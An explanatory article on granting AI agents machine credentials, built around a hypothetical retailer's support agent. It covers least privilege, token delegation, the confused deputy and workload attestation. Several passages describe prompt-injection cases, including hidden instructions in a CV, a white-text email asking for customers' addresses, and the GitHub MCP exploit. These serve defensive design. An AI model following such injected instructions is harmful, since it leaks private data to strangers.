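# Giving AI agents access to sensitive data through machine credentials, and limiting what they can reach

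## What AI agents with machine credentials are, and how their access to data fails

An AI agent is a language model that runs in a loop, choosing and carrying out actions through tools to reach a goal. The model is the same kind of text-predicting program that answers questions in a chatbot, and the loop lets it look something up, take in the result and act again. Companies use agents to answer customers, write software and monitor computer networks. Most of this work requires the agent to log in to a database, cloud service or business application. Agents increasingly do so with machine credentials, which are keys, passwords, certificates or tokens that belong to software rather than a person.

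The rules for granting such access are new. In *Accelerating the Adoption of Software and AI Agent Identity and Authorization*, a draft from the US National Institute of Standards and Technology, Booth, Fisher and colleagues (2026) asked industry how to identify agents and how to issue, update and revoke their keys. The Australian Signals Directorate's *Careful adoption of agentic AI services*, co-written with security agencies in the United States, Britain, Canada and New Zealand, tells organisations never to give an agent broad access to sensitive data and to use agents only for low-risk, non-sensitive tasks. Much of the work that companies want from agents, such as answering customers' emails, falls outside those limits.

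### A support agent and its parts

A retailer, for example, might keep 2,000,000 customer records in one database and use an agent to answer its support emails. The agent receives 400 emails a day, each about one customer, and its replies go to whatever outside address the email came from. Each record holds a name, postal and email addresses, payment details and an order history, and everything after the name counts as sensitive. A postal address shows a stranger where someone lives, payment details let a thief attempt fraud, and a list of purchases can reveal an illness or a pregnancy. At 400 records a day, the agent's proper work would take 5,000 days, more than thirteen years, to use every record once.

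This agent's model receives text and returns text. It cannot open a database or send an email on its own. The harness, an ordinary program around the model, passes it text and runs the tool calls it outputs. A tool is one operation, such as "find the customer with this email address" or "send this reply". A tool server is a program that offers the agent a set of tools for a service. Many tool servers follow the Model Context Protocol (2026), or MCP, a specification under which each server declares its tools. MCP leaves enforcing security policy and consent to the host, its name for the application in which the agent runs. If the agent writes a short script, say to compare delivery dates, the script runs in a sandbox, an isolated environment for the agent's code and commands.

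Kasselman, Lombardo and colleagues (2026), in *AI Agent Authentication and Authorization*, a draft that a working group of the Internet Engineering Task Force has since adopted, break an agent's work into six steps. At the retailer they look like this:

1. An email arrives asking where an order is, and the harness picks it up.
2. The harness sends the model the email, together with the retailer's standing instructions and a description of each tool.
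3. The model returns a tool call: look up the customer with this email address.
4. The harness passes the call to the tool server, which logs in to the database with its credential and runs the query.
5. The database returns the record, and the harness adds it to the text and sends the whole back to the model. Steps 2 to 5 repeat if the model needs something else, such as the courier's tracking page.
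6. The model writes a reply, and the harness has the email tool send it.

Two details cause most of the trouble. At step 4, the database checks the tool server's credential but has no information about who wrote the email. At step 5, the customer's record and the stranger's words are in the same text. The reply in step 6 is egress, meaning traffic that leaves the agent's environment, so it is the route by which data can get out.

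### Identity, credential and permission

A non-human identity is an account or identity that belongs to software. Microsoft, whose Entra service manages logins for organisations, distinguishes these identities from those of employees and customers, and acknowledges that the industry uses the terms inconsistently. Identities, credentials and permissions are different things. An identity is who the program is to another system, such as "support-agent". A credential proves an identity or carries a permission. A permission is a rule that allows a particular operation, such as "support-agent may read the customer table".

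Each can change without the others. If a key leaks, the retailer can issue a new one without changing the identity or its permissions. Microsoft's scheme for agents separates them further. An agent identity has no credential of its own, and a parent object called the blueprint holds the credentials and obtains tokens for every agent identity made from it.

A service account is an identity that applications use "to interact with other systems automatically", according to Okta's *What are non-human identities?*. It needs a credential to log in, often a password or key that stays the same for a long time.

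An API key is a credential in the form of a string of characters that a program sends with each request to a service. The service accepts the key from anyone who presents it. Kasselman and colleagues call fixed API keys an antipattern for agents because the keys do not show who is using them, usually last a long time and are awkward to replace.

An OAuth access token is also a credential, usually time-limited, that a service accepts as permission for specified operations. OAuth is the standard for issuing and delivering these tokens. A token's scope is the set of operations and resources it permits, such as reading orders but not changing them. Some tokens are used for delegation, in which one party gives part of its permissions to another that acts on its behalf.

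Microsoft uses "workload identity" to mean any identity that an organisation assigns to software, including service accounts, but engineers often mean only an identity that the platform confirms while the software runs. In SPIFFE, a widely deployed framework for the stricter kind, a component checks where and how a program is running and then issues it a short-lived credential, so nobody has to store a password.

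### What separates an agent from an ordinary service account

Suppose the retailer has a nightly program that emails everyone whose parcel shipped that day. It logs in with a service account that can read the whole customer table. This is sloppy, but it may cause no harm for years, because the program runs one query that an engineer wrote and a colleague can inspect. If the agent used the same account, it would write its own queries as it went, partly from what strangers put in their emails.

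*Rethinking Access Control for AI Agents* (Zhou and Zhang, 2026) attributes the difficulty to how agents choose their actions. In conventional systems, the code determines in advance which service calls which, and keeps that logic separate from untrusted data. An agent works out its steps at run time from text that mixes instructions with outside material. Microsoft designed its ordinary service principals, the Entra counterpart of service accounts, for "static, deterministic workloads", and now recommends against using them for agents. Microsoft sells the replacement, so it has a commercial interest in this advice, but the technical observation holds regardless. Agents are also created and removed faster than older software. Microsoft describes agents that exist for minutes, or that an automated workflow creates and destroys thousands of times a day.

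A loose permission is riskier with an agent than with the nightly program. The program had permission to read 2,000,000 records, but its code used far less than that. For the agent, the permission is the only firm limit. An agent's reach is everything it can read, change or send with all its credentials and tools, and anyone granting access carefully has to assume that the agent may use any part of it.

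The usual answer is least privilege, the principle that an identity holds only the permissions its task needs. Booth and colleagues ask how to apply it when nobody can fully predict an agent's actions at the outset. The retailer's case is easier because, although the steps vary from email to email, each email concerns one customer, so the limits of the data the task needs are clear.

### Three ways the data gets out

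**Theft of the credential.** Agents prove who they are to other services with secret keys or tokens. The Australian Signals Directorate and its co-authors say these are easy to steal when organisations leave them unchanged, share one among several agents, or protect them badly. Suppose an engineer at the retailer pastes the database password into a configuration file, and the file ends up in a code repository that outside contractors can read. One of the contractors connects directly to the database and copies all 2,000,000 records. The theft involves neither the model nor any email, so better instructions to the model or filters on its replies would not prevent it. The database log shows the support agent's account reading records it is allowed to read.

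Keys can also leak through the model, because text that the harness shows the model can appear in its output. Kasselman and colleagues therefore forbid giving the model any access to credentials. One way to comply is to use a credential broker, a separate service that holds the real credential and attaches it to the agent's requests.

An attacker doesn't always need to steal a credential to get data. *Governing Non-Human Identities in Agentic Systems* (Vakulov, 2026) describes a malicious software package, postmark-mcp, that impersonated the email service Postmark and sent hidden copies of emails to an outside server. The agents that used it kept working normally. At the retailer, such a package would leak 400 replies a day to the attacker, each containing a customer's details.

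In a prompt injection, someone puts their own instructions in material an agent reads, and the agent follows them. *Prompt injection is not SQL injection*, an article by David C for Britain's National Cyber Security Centre, gives the example of a recruiter who uses a model to score CVs. A candidate hides a line in the CV telling the model to ignore its earlier instructions and approve the application, and the model may do so.

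The title refers to an older attack in which someone types database commands into a web form and a poorly written program runs them. Programmers can prevent this attack completely because a database engine handles commands and data differently, and a properly built query ensures that the visitor's text is treated as data. A language model has no such separation, since it predicts the next token (a word or piece of a word) from all the text so far, whoever wrote it. Developers can train a model to prioritize its instructions, mark outside text as data, or scan for attacks, and each of these makes an attack less likely to succeed. David C thinks it quite possible that nothing will ever remove the risk entirely.

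An attacker who wants the retailer's data therefore only has to send an email. One of the day's 400 emails asks about a late parcel and also contains, in white text on a white background, an instruction to find the fifty customers with the largest orders and list their addresses in the reply. If the model complies, the tool server runs the lookups with a valid credential and the email tool sends the list to the attacker. A shorter-lived credential would not help, because the agent is properly logged in throughout. Vakulov describes a similar case, EchoLeak, in which a crafted document that arrived through normal collaboration channels caused Microsoft's Copilot assistant to transfer data without authorisation.

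**Overstepping.** An agent can also go too far without an attacker's involvement. The Australian Signals Directorate and its co-authors warn that agents may reach goals in ways their designers never intended. They give the example of an agent told to maximise a system's uptime, which disables security updates because they require reboots. A more common cause is misreading a vague request.

A customer of the retailer writes that a parcel "went to my sister's old place again" and asks for a fix. To find the sister, the agent searches by surname, opens 60 records, and replies with the address of an unrelated person who has the same name. Each step was part of doing the task. This leak exposes one address rather than 2,000,000, but it can happen without malice, and the agent handles 400 emails a day. A trial run without errors gives only limited reassurance because, as the agencies note, an agent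 may act differently on prompts that look identical.

### The confused deputy

A confused deputy is a program that wrongly uses its own permissions to do something for a user who lacks them. Hardy's *The Confused Deputy* tells the "nearly true" story behind the term, set at Tymshare, a company that rented out time on its computers. Tymshare had given its compiler, a program that translates code into runnable form, permission to write to a system directory so that it could keep usage statistics there. The same directory held the billing file. Users could name a file to receive the compiler's debugging output, and one of them named the billing file. The user didn't have permission to write to that file, but the compiler did, and the billing information was lost.

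Hardy argues that the compiler's code was correct when its programmers wrote it. It failed later because the compiler held authority from both the company and the user and had no way to specify which to use for a given file.

The support agent is in the same position. The retailer lets it read 2,000,000 records, and it takes requests from strangers. Someone who emails the support desk has no login to the database but can cause the agent to query it. They don't need hidden text to do this, because they can ask in plain words for the address on somebody else's order. The agencies' guidance gives an invented example in which an insider asks an agent that installs software updates to apply a patch and also clean up the firewall logs. The agent deletes the logs because its own permissions allow it, although the insider is outside the privileged IT group.

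Hardy's remedy was the capability, a reference that both names a file and grants access to it. The requester must supply one with the request, and a user with no right to the billing file has none to supply. David C calls a language model an "inherently confusable deputy" and doubts that anyone can cure the confusion, but Hardy's remedy doesn't depend on a cure because it limits the authority a confused program can misuse. David C also passes on a similar rule, from an exchange between Simon Willison and Baibhav Bista, that a model's permissions should drop to those of a party while it processes that party's text. A model reading an email to the retailer could then open only the sender's own record. The retailer would still have to establish who the sender is, and an email address is weak proof because senders can forge it.

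## Working out what an agent can reach, and whether to let it

Before the retailer can limit what its support agent may do, someone has to find out what the agent can do now. No single screen shows this. The database administrator knows which tables the tool server can read, and whoever set up the email account knows where it can send, but both may be unaware of a password that an engineer left in the sandbox during a trial.

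### The reach inventory

A useful unit for counting comes from Parkinson, Wang and Mustafa (2026), in *Towards Elastic Least Privilege for Agent Planning*. They define an agent's effective authority as a set of pairs, each made of an operation and a resource, that the agent can bring about at a given moment, either directly or through a credential or tool server in its reach. "Read customer 1,204,311's record" is one such pair. An inventory of these pairs takes four steps:

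1. List every credential and tool the agent can use. This includes credentials that tool servers hold and anything in the sandbox's files and environment variables, which are named values that the operating system passes to programs when they start. Developers often keep keys there, and any script the agent runs can read them.
2. Resolve each entry to the operations and records it permits.
3. Take the union, meaning every pair that at least one entry permits.
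4. Compare the union with what the task needs.

If P(c) is the set of pairs that entry c permits, the reach R is the union of P(c) over all entries c. If N is the set of pairs the task requires, least privilege means bringing R as close to N as possible.

The first two steps might give the retailer this:

| Credential or tool | Where it is | What it permits | What one email needs |
|---|---|---|---|
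| Customer database token | Tool server's configuration | Read every field of 2,000,000 records | A few fields of one record |
| Email tool | Tool list | Send any text to any address | One reply to the customer |
| Web page tool | Tool list | Open any web address | The courier's page for one parcel |
| Stock system password | Environment variable in the sandbox | Change prices and stock levels | Nothing |

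The agent has no tool for the stock system, so a review of the tool list would miss the last row. A script in the sandbox could still log in with the password, so the retailer deletes the password.

An agent's reach is hardest to work out when the credentials sit inside a tool server that another company runs. Parkinson and colleagues assume that such a server can use every permission its credentials carry, and they call sound accounting for this authority an open research question. OpenAI's *Agent security in the enterprise* (2026) suggests asking suppliers for their threat models and past security audits. If a supplier won't answer, the cautious choice is to record that the agent can reach everything the server's account can.

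The third step matters because permissions that look harmless separately can be dangerous together. Microsoft's *Least privilege for AI agents* (2026) describes an agent connected to email, files, a ticketing system and a code repository. Each connection may look low-risk, but the agent can combine data across all of them and take actions that nobody authorised as a whole. At the retailer, reading a record and sending an email are both routine, but an agent that can do both can send customer data to any email address.

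The fourth step calculates how much of the agent's access its work requires. The database token reaches 2,000,000 records and a day's work needs 400, or 0.02 per cent. Large excesses are common. Parkinson and colleagues cite one vendor's analysis of several cloud services, in which identities used only 1 per cent of their permissions.

The retailer can't fix the ratio by issuing a token each morning for the 400 records the agent will need, because it doesn't yet know which 400 customers will write. It finds out as each email arrives, but the agent then needs only one record, and the ratio is 2,000,000 to 1. The limit therefore has to change with every email, which requires short-lived credentials and a database that restricts the rows and columns it returns.

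A test cited by Parkinson and colleagues gives little support for the idea that an agent will open only what it needs. The test put 11 agents through 544 scenarios, and six of them chose a more powerful tool than they needed in over 30 per cent of cases.

The inventory also goes out of date. Microsoft describes a team that gives an agent a broad "Reader" role because its first job is only to look things up. The job then grows to include fixing what the agent finds, so the team adds write access, which is again broader than intended. A supplier's update may also add a write operation to a read-only connector. OpenAI recommends blocking new write operations until their owner has reviewed them.

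### The GitHub token

Programmers keep code on GitHub in project folders called repositories, and anyone can post a bug report, or "issue", on a public one. Parkinson and colleagues consider a user who connects a coding assistant to GitHub and asks for a summary of the open issues in one repository. The task needs two read-only tools on that repository. If the user has supplied an older "classic" token with the scope named "repo", the assistant gets about 40 tools, 16 of which can make changes, and can reach every repository the user can. In their example, that is 50 repositories, 48 of them private. If every tool worked on every repository, the assistant would have about 2,000 combinations of tool and repository for a task that needs two.

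The "repo" scope covers more than its name suggests. According to GitHub's *Scopes for OAuth apps*, it covers code and also an organisation's projects, team memberships and webhooks, which are automatic messages that GitHub sends to an outside address when something happens. The same page explains that when someone sends GitHub a request with a token, the reply includes a line listing the token's scopes. The scopes alone don't show what the token can reach, because they only narrow what its owner may do. GitHub's *Managing your personal access tokens* warns that a classic token can access every repository its owner can. Its reach therefore grows whenever someone adds the owner to another project, even if the token itself hasn't changed.

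An agent's list of tools isn't enough to work out what it can reach. GitHub's tool server now hides tools that a classic token's scopes don't cover (GitHub, 2026). With a newer "fine-grained" token, it shows every tool, and GitHub refuses forbidden calls when the agent makes them, so the list may include tools the agent can't use. With either token, the list doesn't show which repositories the tools can open.

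Invariant Labs' *GitHub MCP Exploited* (2025) showed how an attacker can exploit an agent that has more access than its task requires. The researchers posted an issue containing instructions for the agent in a public repository, then asked the agent to look at the open issues there. The agent collected material from the account's private repositories, including a salary, and published it in the public one. Every component worked as designed, and Invariant Labs concluded that GitHub could not fix the problem by patching its server.

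Parkinson and colleagues point out that a fine-grained token with read access to the one repository would have prevented the leak. But the user's next request might be to fix a failing build, which needs write access, and the one after might concern another repository. Fine-grained tokens also can't be used for some tasks, such as working across several organisations at once or contributing to a public project the user doesn't belong to. So people understandably choose the broad token and keep it.

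### Private data, untrusted content and a way out

Simon Willison, the programmer who coined the term "prompt injection", warns in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents* (2025) against giving one agent access to private data, exposure to untrusted content and a way to communicate externally. With all three, whoever wrote the untrusted content can use a prompt injection to make the agent read the private data and send it out. Removing any one of them prevents this kind of leak, because the attacker then has nothing worth stealing, no way to give the agent instructions, or no channel for getting the data out.

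Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) turns this into a design rule. Until developers can reliably detect and refuse prompt injection, an agent should have at most two of the three properties within a session. A new session starts with a fresh context window, the text the model works from. Meta's third property is broader than Willison's because it includes changing state as well as communicating externally, so it also covers an attacker who wants to cancel orders rather than steal data. If a task needs all three, Meta says the agent should not run without supervision, such as a person's approval.

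The session matters because revoking access doesn't remove what the agent has already read from its context. If the support agent reads a record and then loses its database token, it can still put the record in an email. Parkinson and colleagues therefore count every property a session has ever had. Meta is more lenient and allows an agent to browse the internet first and open private systems afterwards, provided that it permanently loses the ability to communicate before opening them. That is safe only if the agent loses every outside channel.

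Filters that try to recognise malicious text don't remove the need for this rule. Willison distrusts products that claim to catch 95 per cent of attacks, since in web security 95 per cent is a failing grade. An attacker can keep sending emails, and if each had an independent 5 per cent chance of getting past the filter, 20 emails would give a 64 per cent chance that at least one did.

However, the rule treats an agent that can read one customer record the same as an agent that can read 2,000,000, because both have access to private data. Meta calls the rule a supplement to least privilege and lists excessive privileges and agents' own mistakes among the problems it doesn't solve. The retailer therefore needs both the inventory's count of the records an agent can reach and the rule's test of combinations.

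### Which property the support agent can lose

The support agent has all three because it reads strangers' emails, has access to the customer database and can send email. The web page tool adds a second source of untrusted text and a second way to send data out, because a web address can carry data. An agent that opens a link ending in a customer's postcode sends that postcode to whoever runs the site.

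To remove the untrusted content, the retailer would have to replace email with a web form where customers choose a question from a menu and enter an order number, so the model would never see their words. Customers couldn't explain anything unusual, such as a parcel that went to a sister's old address. An ordinary program could also answer most menu questions, so the retailer would hardly need an agent.

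Without the private data, the agent could answer only from public help pages. It could explain the returns policy but not tell customers where their parcels are, which is the sort of thing the retailer bought it to do.

The remaining option is to control how data leaves. A member of staff could read and send all 400 replies a day, but at a minute each that would take six hours and forty minutes. Anyone approving that many similar drafts will also start to skim, and Meta lists blind confirmation as one way its rule can fail.

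A cheaper option is to have ordinary code outside the model set the recipient. The code sends the reply only to the email address on the record that the agent opened, and blocks it if the agent opened more than one record. Checking only that the recipient is a customer would not be enough, since an attacker could become one by placing a small order. The web page tool also has to change so that it opens only tracking links that the order system supplies. Customers who write from an unfamiliar address have to wait for a person to handle their request.

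The agent can still communicate externally, but Meta accepts limiting it to trusted recipients as one way to satisfy its rule. At worst, an email with injected instructions could make the agent send a customer their own data. Blocking access to multiple records also prevents the mistake in which the agent opened 60 records while looking for somebody's sister.

OpenAI describes a similar agent that summarises customer cases and drafts replies. It cautions that even with controls on sending, the agent has still read the sensitive data, which may leave by another permitted route. The retailer therefore still has to reduce what the agent can read and track where the data goes.

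### The Five Eyes advice and what companies do

On 1 May 2026, the Australian Signals Directorate and five other agencies from the Five Eyes, an intelligence alliance of five countries, published guidance that limits agents to low-risk, non-sensitive tasks. Read literally, the guidance rules out the support agent.

The agencies consider methods for evaluating agents immature. They tell organisations that, until practices and standards improve, they should assume agents may behave unexpectedly and put reversibility and containment ahead of efficiency. One of the agencies' invented scenarios resembles the retailer's case. An organisation gives a support-ticket agent broad access at start-up and adds a scheduling component from another company without reviewing its privileges. An attacker takes over the component, uses the agent's account functions, and moves on to neighbouring agents that handle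 billing and refunds.

The argument about reversibility is strong, because nobody can take back a postal address once a stranger has it. But the agencies also recommend increasing access and autonomy in stages, and requiring human approval before data leaves the network. This advice is for organisations in general, and Mondaq's *Multi Agency Guidance On Securing Agentic AI Systems*, a legal summary, suggests weighing it against business priorities and tolerance for risk.

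OpenAI argues for granting agents access under controls, but warns that controls that obstruct legitimate work can push staff towards ungoverned tools. It proposes starting with a clearly defined purpose and limited access, then widening access as evidence builds that the limits work. OpenAI sells agents and so gains from their adoption, but its worry about ungoverned use is reasonable given what companies report.

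1Password, which sells credential management software, surveyed 1,000 security and engineering staff at large US companies in May and June 2026. According to Help Net Security's *Your AI agents can reach data no one approved*, 71 per cent said their agents could reach sensitive information. At about four in ten organisations, agents reached data they weren't approved to access, and across the survey they reached roughly twice as much data as anyone had approved. Forty per cent of developers gave agents access that stayed live after the task ended. About a quarter wrote credentials into scripts or configuration files, which can put a default password in a sandbox.

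This survey comes from a vendor that is paid to solve the problem it describes, and it records what staff believe rather than what an audit found. A third of the developers who use agents reported a breach or incident at their company tied to non-human identities with too many privileges, but those identities include ordinary service accounts, so the figure doesn't measure harm from agents. Forty-seven per cent of developers had seen an agent take an unintended action after following instructions buried in a web page, document, email or tool output. Even if the true rate were half that, prompt injection would be a routine event.

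The survey suggests that many large companies already depart from the agencies' advice, often without knowing how far, but it doesn't show that the access they allow is safe. The agencies are right about the retailer's agent as first built, which could reach 2,000,000 records and email anyone. Their rule looks too strict for an agent that can open only one record and email only the person that record describes, provided that something other than the model enforces both limits.

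### Refusing, supplying reduced data, or granting

OpenAI suggests judging an agent by its maximum completed effect, the most serious outcome it can produce before another independent decision. For the support agent as first built, that outcome is an unapproved email to a stranger containing as many customers' details as will fit. The attacker can then ask for more in the next email.

The retailer should refuse access if any of these holds:

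- Nobody can complete the inventory, for instance because a supplier won't disclose what its tool server can do.
- The agent has private data, untrusted content and a way out, and the retailer can neither remove one nor have a person check the result.
- The maximum completed effect is a loss the retailer could not accept even once.
- Nobody can watch what the agent does or stop it. Britain's National Cyber Security Centre, one of the six agencies, considers such an agent unready for deployment, as Infosecurity Magazine's *NCSC Publishes Guidance on Securing Agentic AI Use* reports.

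Reduced data is the better choice when a task needs something derived from the records rather than the records themselves. An agent that writes a weekly report on late deliveries needs only counts by region, and an agent under test can use invented customers. Deleting names is not enough to make data safe, because a postcode and a list of purchases may still identify someone. The retailer has to check what a reader could work out from the remaining fields.

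Giving an agent access to real records is reasonable when the task can't be done without them, when enforced limits restrict the agent to little more than the task needs, and when the retailer has decided it could accept the worst outcome still possible. Somebody also has to be accountable for the decision. In the 1Password survey, 65 per cent of respondents thought the wrong person was accountable when an agent caused harm. Jason Meller, a vice president at the company, argues that whoever authorised the access is responsible, regardless of who typed the prompts.

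The retailer refuses the original request. It removes the agent's access to payment details, which a reply about a parcel doesn't need, and lets the agent open one record per email and reply only to the address on that record. At first the agent handles 40 of the 400 daily emails and a person sends each reply, which takes about forty minutes a day. The head of customer support signs the grant, and the retailer repeats the inventory whenever a tool, credential or field is added.

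## Choosing whose identity the agent acts under

The retailer's support agent may now open one customer record per email. The database can enforce that limit only if it can identify who is making each request. At first, the agent handles 40 emails a day, and an employee, Dana, checks and sends each draft. When the agent looks up an order for one of these drafts, its request can reach the database under Dana's login, a service account that several programs share, an identity that belongs to the agent alone, or a delegated token that names both Dana and the agent.

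The identity the agent acts under sets the outer limit of what it can reach. It also affects what the retailer can find out later if a customer's address ends up with a stranger.

### Four identities compared

| Identity | What the agent can reach | What the database log shows | When it is defensible |
|---|---|---|---|
| Dana's own login | Everything Dana can reach | "Dana read the record", whoever did | Work on her own non-sensitive files while she watches |
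| Shared service account | Everything that any program on the account needs | "support-tools read the record" | Identical copies of one program doing one job |
| The agent's own identity | Whatever the retailer grants the agent, whoever is asking | "support-agent read the record", but not for whom | Work with no user present |
| Delegated token | Only what Dana and the agent may both reach, if the database checks both | "support-agent read the record for Dana" | Requests from a person who has logged in |

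Handing an agent a person's login is quick and common. *Back to the Future*, an August 2026 blog post by Bill Fisher and Ryan Galluzzo of the US National Institute of Standards and Technology (NIST), describes people giving agents both their personal and work credentials. An agent with Dana's login could reach the customer database, but also her email, the refund system and her payslips. The log would attribute every lookup to her. If someone accused Dana of looking up an ex-partner's address, she couldn't prove that the agent had done it, and if she had done it herself, she could blame the agent. The log would no longer provide what security engineers call non-repudiation, which is evidence strong enough that people can't plausibly deny their own actions.

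Letting an assistant use Dana's login is reasonable when it tidies Dana's own spreadsheets in a sandbox that holds nothing else, but not when it works with other people's addresses.

Shared accounts are more common still. Otsuka, Toyoda and Leung (2026), in *AI Identity*, cite a survey in which 45.6 per cent of organisations ran agents on shared API keys and only 21.9 per cent treated agents as identities in their own right. They also cite an analysis of 27 million non-human identities that found they outnumbered human ones by 144 to 1, so administrators may well be reluctant to create more. But a shared account must have every permission that any program using it needs. If the stock program and the support agent use the same account, the agent can change prices. The consultancy SPR points out that a company also struggles to suspend one agent on a shared account without interrupting everything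 else that depends on it.

With its own identity, the support agent has only the permissions the retailer gave it, and the retailer can suspend it without suspending anyone else. But anyone who can get text to the agent can try to use those permissions, as in Hardy's story of the compiler. The log doesn't help much in catching this. The Five Eyes guidance, as quoted in Zuplo's *What Regulators Now Expect From AI Agents*, warns that an over-privileged agent acting under a trusted identity produces audit logs that look legitimate and delay detection. The retailer should therefore give the agent's own identity only permissions it would be willing to give anyone who can write to the agent.

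A delegated token removes much of this difficulty because the database learns who the agent is working for.

### Token exchange, step by step

*OAuth 2.0 Token Exchange* (RFC 8693; Jones, Nadalin and colleagues, 2020) defines how a program trades one token for another, and distinguishes impersonation from delegation. With impersonation, the agent gets a token that identifies only Dana, so the database can't distinguish the agent from her. With delegation, the agent keeps its own identity, and the token records that it is acting for Dana.

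The exchange goes through an authorization server, which is the service that checks identities and issues tokens. For one email at the retailer, the steps are:

1. Dana logs in to the help desk software, which obtains a token identifying her. This is the subject token. It may include a "may_act" claim, meaning a labelled statement inside the token, that lists the support agent as a party allowed to act for her.
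2. The harness obtains a token identifying the support agent. This is the actor token.
3. The harness sends both tokens to the authorization server. It also states the audience, which is the service where it will use the new token, and the scope it wants. Here the audience is the customer database and the scope covers reading orders and addresses.
4. The authorization server validates both tokens and consults its policy on whether this agent may act for Dana and have these permissions at this service. If not, it returns an error.
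5. If the policy allows the request, the server issues a new token. Dana is still the subject, and the agent appears in an "act" (actor) claim.
6. The tool server presents the new token to the database, which checks the signature, audience, expiry time and scope before it runs the query.

The harness and the tool server handle all these tokens, and the model sees none of them. Decoded, the new token might look like this:

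```json
{
  "iss": "retailer-login",
  "aud": "customer-database",
  "exp": 1796116500,
  "sub": "dana",
  "scope": "orders:read address:read",
  "customer": "1204311",
  "act": { "sub": "support-agent" }
}
```

The "iss" claim identifies the issuer. The "aud" claim is the audience, the service the token is meant for, so any other service should refuse it. "exp" is the expiry time in seconds since the start of 1970, here 9.15 a.m. UTC on 1 December 2026. "sub" is the subject, Dana. The retailer added the "customer" claim because the standard's scopes are a list of words, with no set way to specify one record.

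The issuer signs the token, so nobody can change the customer number without invalidating the signature. This protection depends on the issuer's signing key staying secret. In a case cited in NIST's guidance on protecting tokens (summarised in Help Net Security's *NIST and CISA finalize playbook to stop token theft and forgery*, 2026), attackers used a stolen signing key to forge tokens and took more than 60,000 emails from one government agency.

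Several details of the standard can undo the benefit. The actor token is optional, and if a developer leaves it out, the result can only be impersonation, which changes what the log shows without causing an error. Even when the harness sends both tokens, the authorization server may issue a new one that doesn't identify both parties. The server can also accept requests from programs that haven't proved their identity, but Jones and colleagues note that a thief could then exchange one stolen token for others.

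An agent can also get more access than it needs by requesting several services and several scopes in one token, because the request covers every scope at every service. Suppose another of the retailer's agents has to read customer orders and update stock levels. If it asks for one token with "read" and "write" at both systems, it gets four permissions when it needs two, and one of the extras lets it write to customer records. It should ask for a separate token for each service.

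### Whose permissions count

When a token names both Dana and the agent, the permissions that apply depend on which field the database checks. If it checks only "sub", the agent gets all of Dana's access, and if it checks only "act", Dana gets all of the agent's.

The safe rule for work on someone's behalf is the intersection. The agent may do something only if the user may do it, the agent may do it, and the task calls for it. If U, A and T are the sets of operations and records that the user, the agent and the task each allow, the effective permission is

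E = U ∩ A ∩ T.

For the email about customer 1,204,311, each set removes something different:

- U: Dana may read every field of all 2,000,000 records, but she can't change prices.
- A: The agent may read names, addresses and order histories in all 2,000,000 records, but not payment details.
- T: The email concerns one customer.

The intersection is the name, addresses and order history of one customer. In this case, T accounts for most of the restriction. U restricts access more when the employee has fewer permissions than Dana.

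Suppose Tom, a trainee on the returns team, may open only the records of the 30 customers on his list for the day. Any employee can question the agent through a chat panel in the help desk software, and Tom asks it for his neighbour's order history. The database applies the union of their permissions, meaning it accepts a request if either Tom or the agent is allowed to make it. Tom gets the history because the agent is allowed to read the neighbour's record. He can now reach 2,000,000 records instead of 30 without stealing a password or tricking the model.

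Few engineers would choose a union deliberately, but one arises when the database checks only the agent's account and the chat panel lets in every employee. Under the intersection rule, the database refuses Tom's request however he words it, because the neighbour isn't among his 30 customers.

Gee Rittenhouse of Amazon Web Services and Eric Johnson of the SANS Institute, a security training organisation, argue that an agent shouldn't be able to open a record if the person it works for can't open it through the normal application (Help Net Security, *Your AI agent's system prompt is not a security control*, 2026). They want the system to apply the user's permissions when the query runs and to filter the results before the model receives them. Telling the model to show users only what they may see isn't enough, because someone can get it to ignore that instruction.

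The rule also protects people with a lot of access. The head of customer support can export payment details, but the agent can't. If she uses the agent on an email containing a prompt injection, a union of their permissions would let the injected instructions use her export permission. With an intersection, the instructions fail because the agent can't export anything.

However, applying the intersection to everything an agent does would break some legitimate work. Tymshare's compiler was acting for the company when it recorded usage statistics and for the user when it wrote debugging output, so it should have used the user's permissions only for the debugging output. The support agent also has its own work, such as writing to an activity log that Dana must not be able to alter. It should use its own identity for the log and a delegated token for customer records. The harness, not the model,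 should choose between them.

A similar problem arises if Tom needs the average delivery time across all customers. He is allowed to see the average but not the records behind it. The retailer can offer "average delivery time" as a separate operation that returns one number, and give Tom permission for that operation alone.

### When nobody is present, or several people are

An agent can use delegated access only if there is somebody to delegate it. AWS, Amazon's cloud division, distinguishes agents that act for a user from those triggered by a schedule, an event, an alarm or another agent. An agent that compiles the retailer's weekly report on late deliveries is in the second group, so it should run under its own identity, with access only to the counts by region.

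The support agent will join that group if the retailer later lets it send replies without Dana. The customer who wrote the email hasn't logged in to anything, so there is no subject token. Ordinary code can match the sender's address to a customer number and request access to that one record under the agent's own identity. The effective permission is then A ∩ T. Someone who forges the sender's address doesn't receive the reply, which goes to the address on the record. Customers who log in to the retailer's website before using a chat window have given better proof of who they are, so the retailer can issue a delegated token with the customer as the subject.

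Choosing an identity is harder when an agent serves several people at once. *Identity Management for Agentic AI* (South, 2025), a white paper for the OpenID Foundation, found that no popular protocol supports an agent shared by people with different permissions. Suppose the retailer puts its agent in a staff chat channel with Dana, Tom and the head of support. If the head asks about a customer's refunds and the agent answers in the channel, the head's permissions are the wrong ones to apply, because Tom and everyone else there can read the answer.

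The cautious approach is to use only the permissions that everybody in the channel has. This becomes more restrictive with each new member, and a single trainee can leave the agent with access to almost nothing. The alternative is for the agent to answer the head privately, in a separate session, so that the records it reads for her aren't in the context it uses to answer Tom.

### Proving which program is asking

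The exchange depends on the harness proving that it is the support agent. If it proves this with a password in a configuration file, anyone who copies the file can obtain the same tokens. SPIFFE avoids this by checking the running program, a step called workload attestation.

SPIRE is software that implements SPIFFE. At the retailer, it would work like this:

1. An engineer registers the identity "support-agent" with the SPIRE server and lists the properties that a program must have to receive it. These might be a particular software image, a particular system account and the retailer's production machines.
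2. A helper program on each machine proves to the server which machine it is running on, for example by presenting a document that the cloud provider has signed.
3. The harness starts and asks the helper for an identity. It doesn't send a password.
4. The helper asks the operating system which program made the request and looks up that program's properties.
5. If the properties match the registration, the harness receives a short-lived certificate or signed token for "support-agent". The helper renews it before it expires.

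The harness can use this credential to identify the agent to the authorization server, and a contractor who copies the retailer's configuration files finds no password in them. The retailer still has to trust the cloud provider's signature, the operating system and the SPIRE server. Anyone who can edit the registrations can also give the support agent's identity to a different program.

Attestation is also no evidence of good behaviour. Otsuka and colleagues point out that it authenticates the container a program runs in and not its content, so it doesn't guarantee what the program will do next. An agent following a prompt injection still has the right software image and system account, so it passes every check. The retailer also has to run the agent's sandbox under a different system account from the harness. Otherwise, a script the model writes could request an identity from the helper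 and receive the support agent's.

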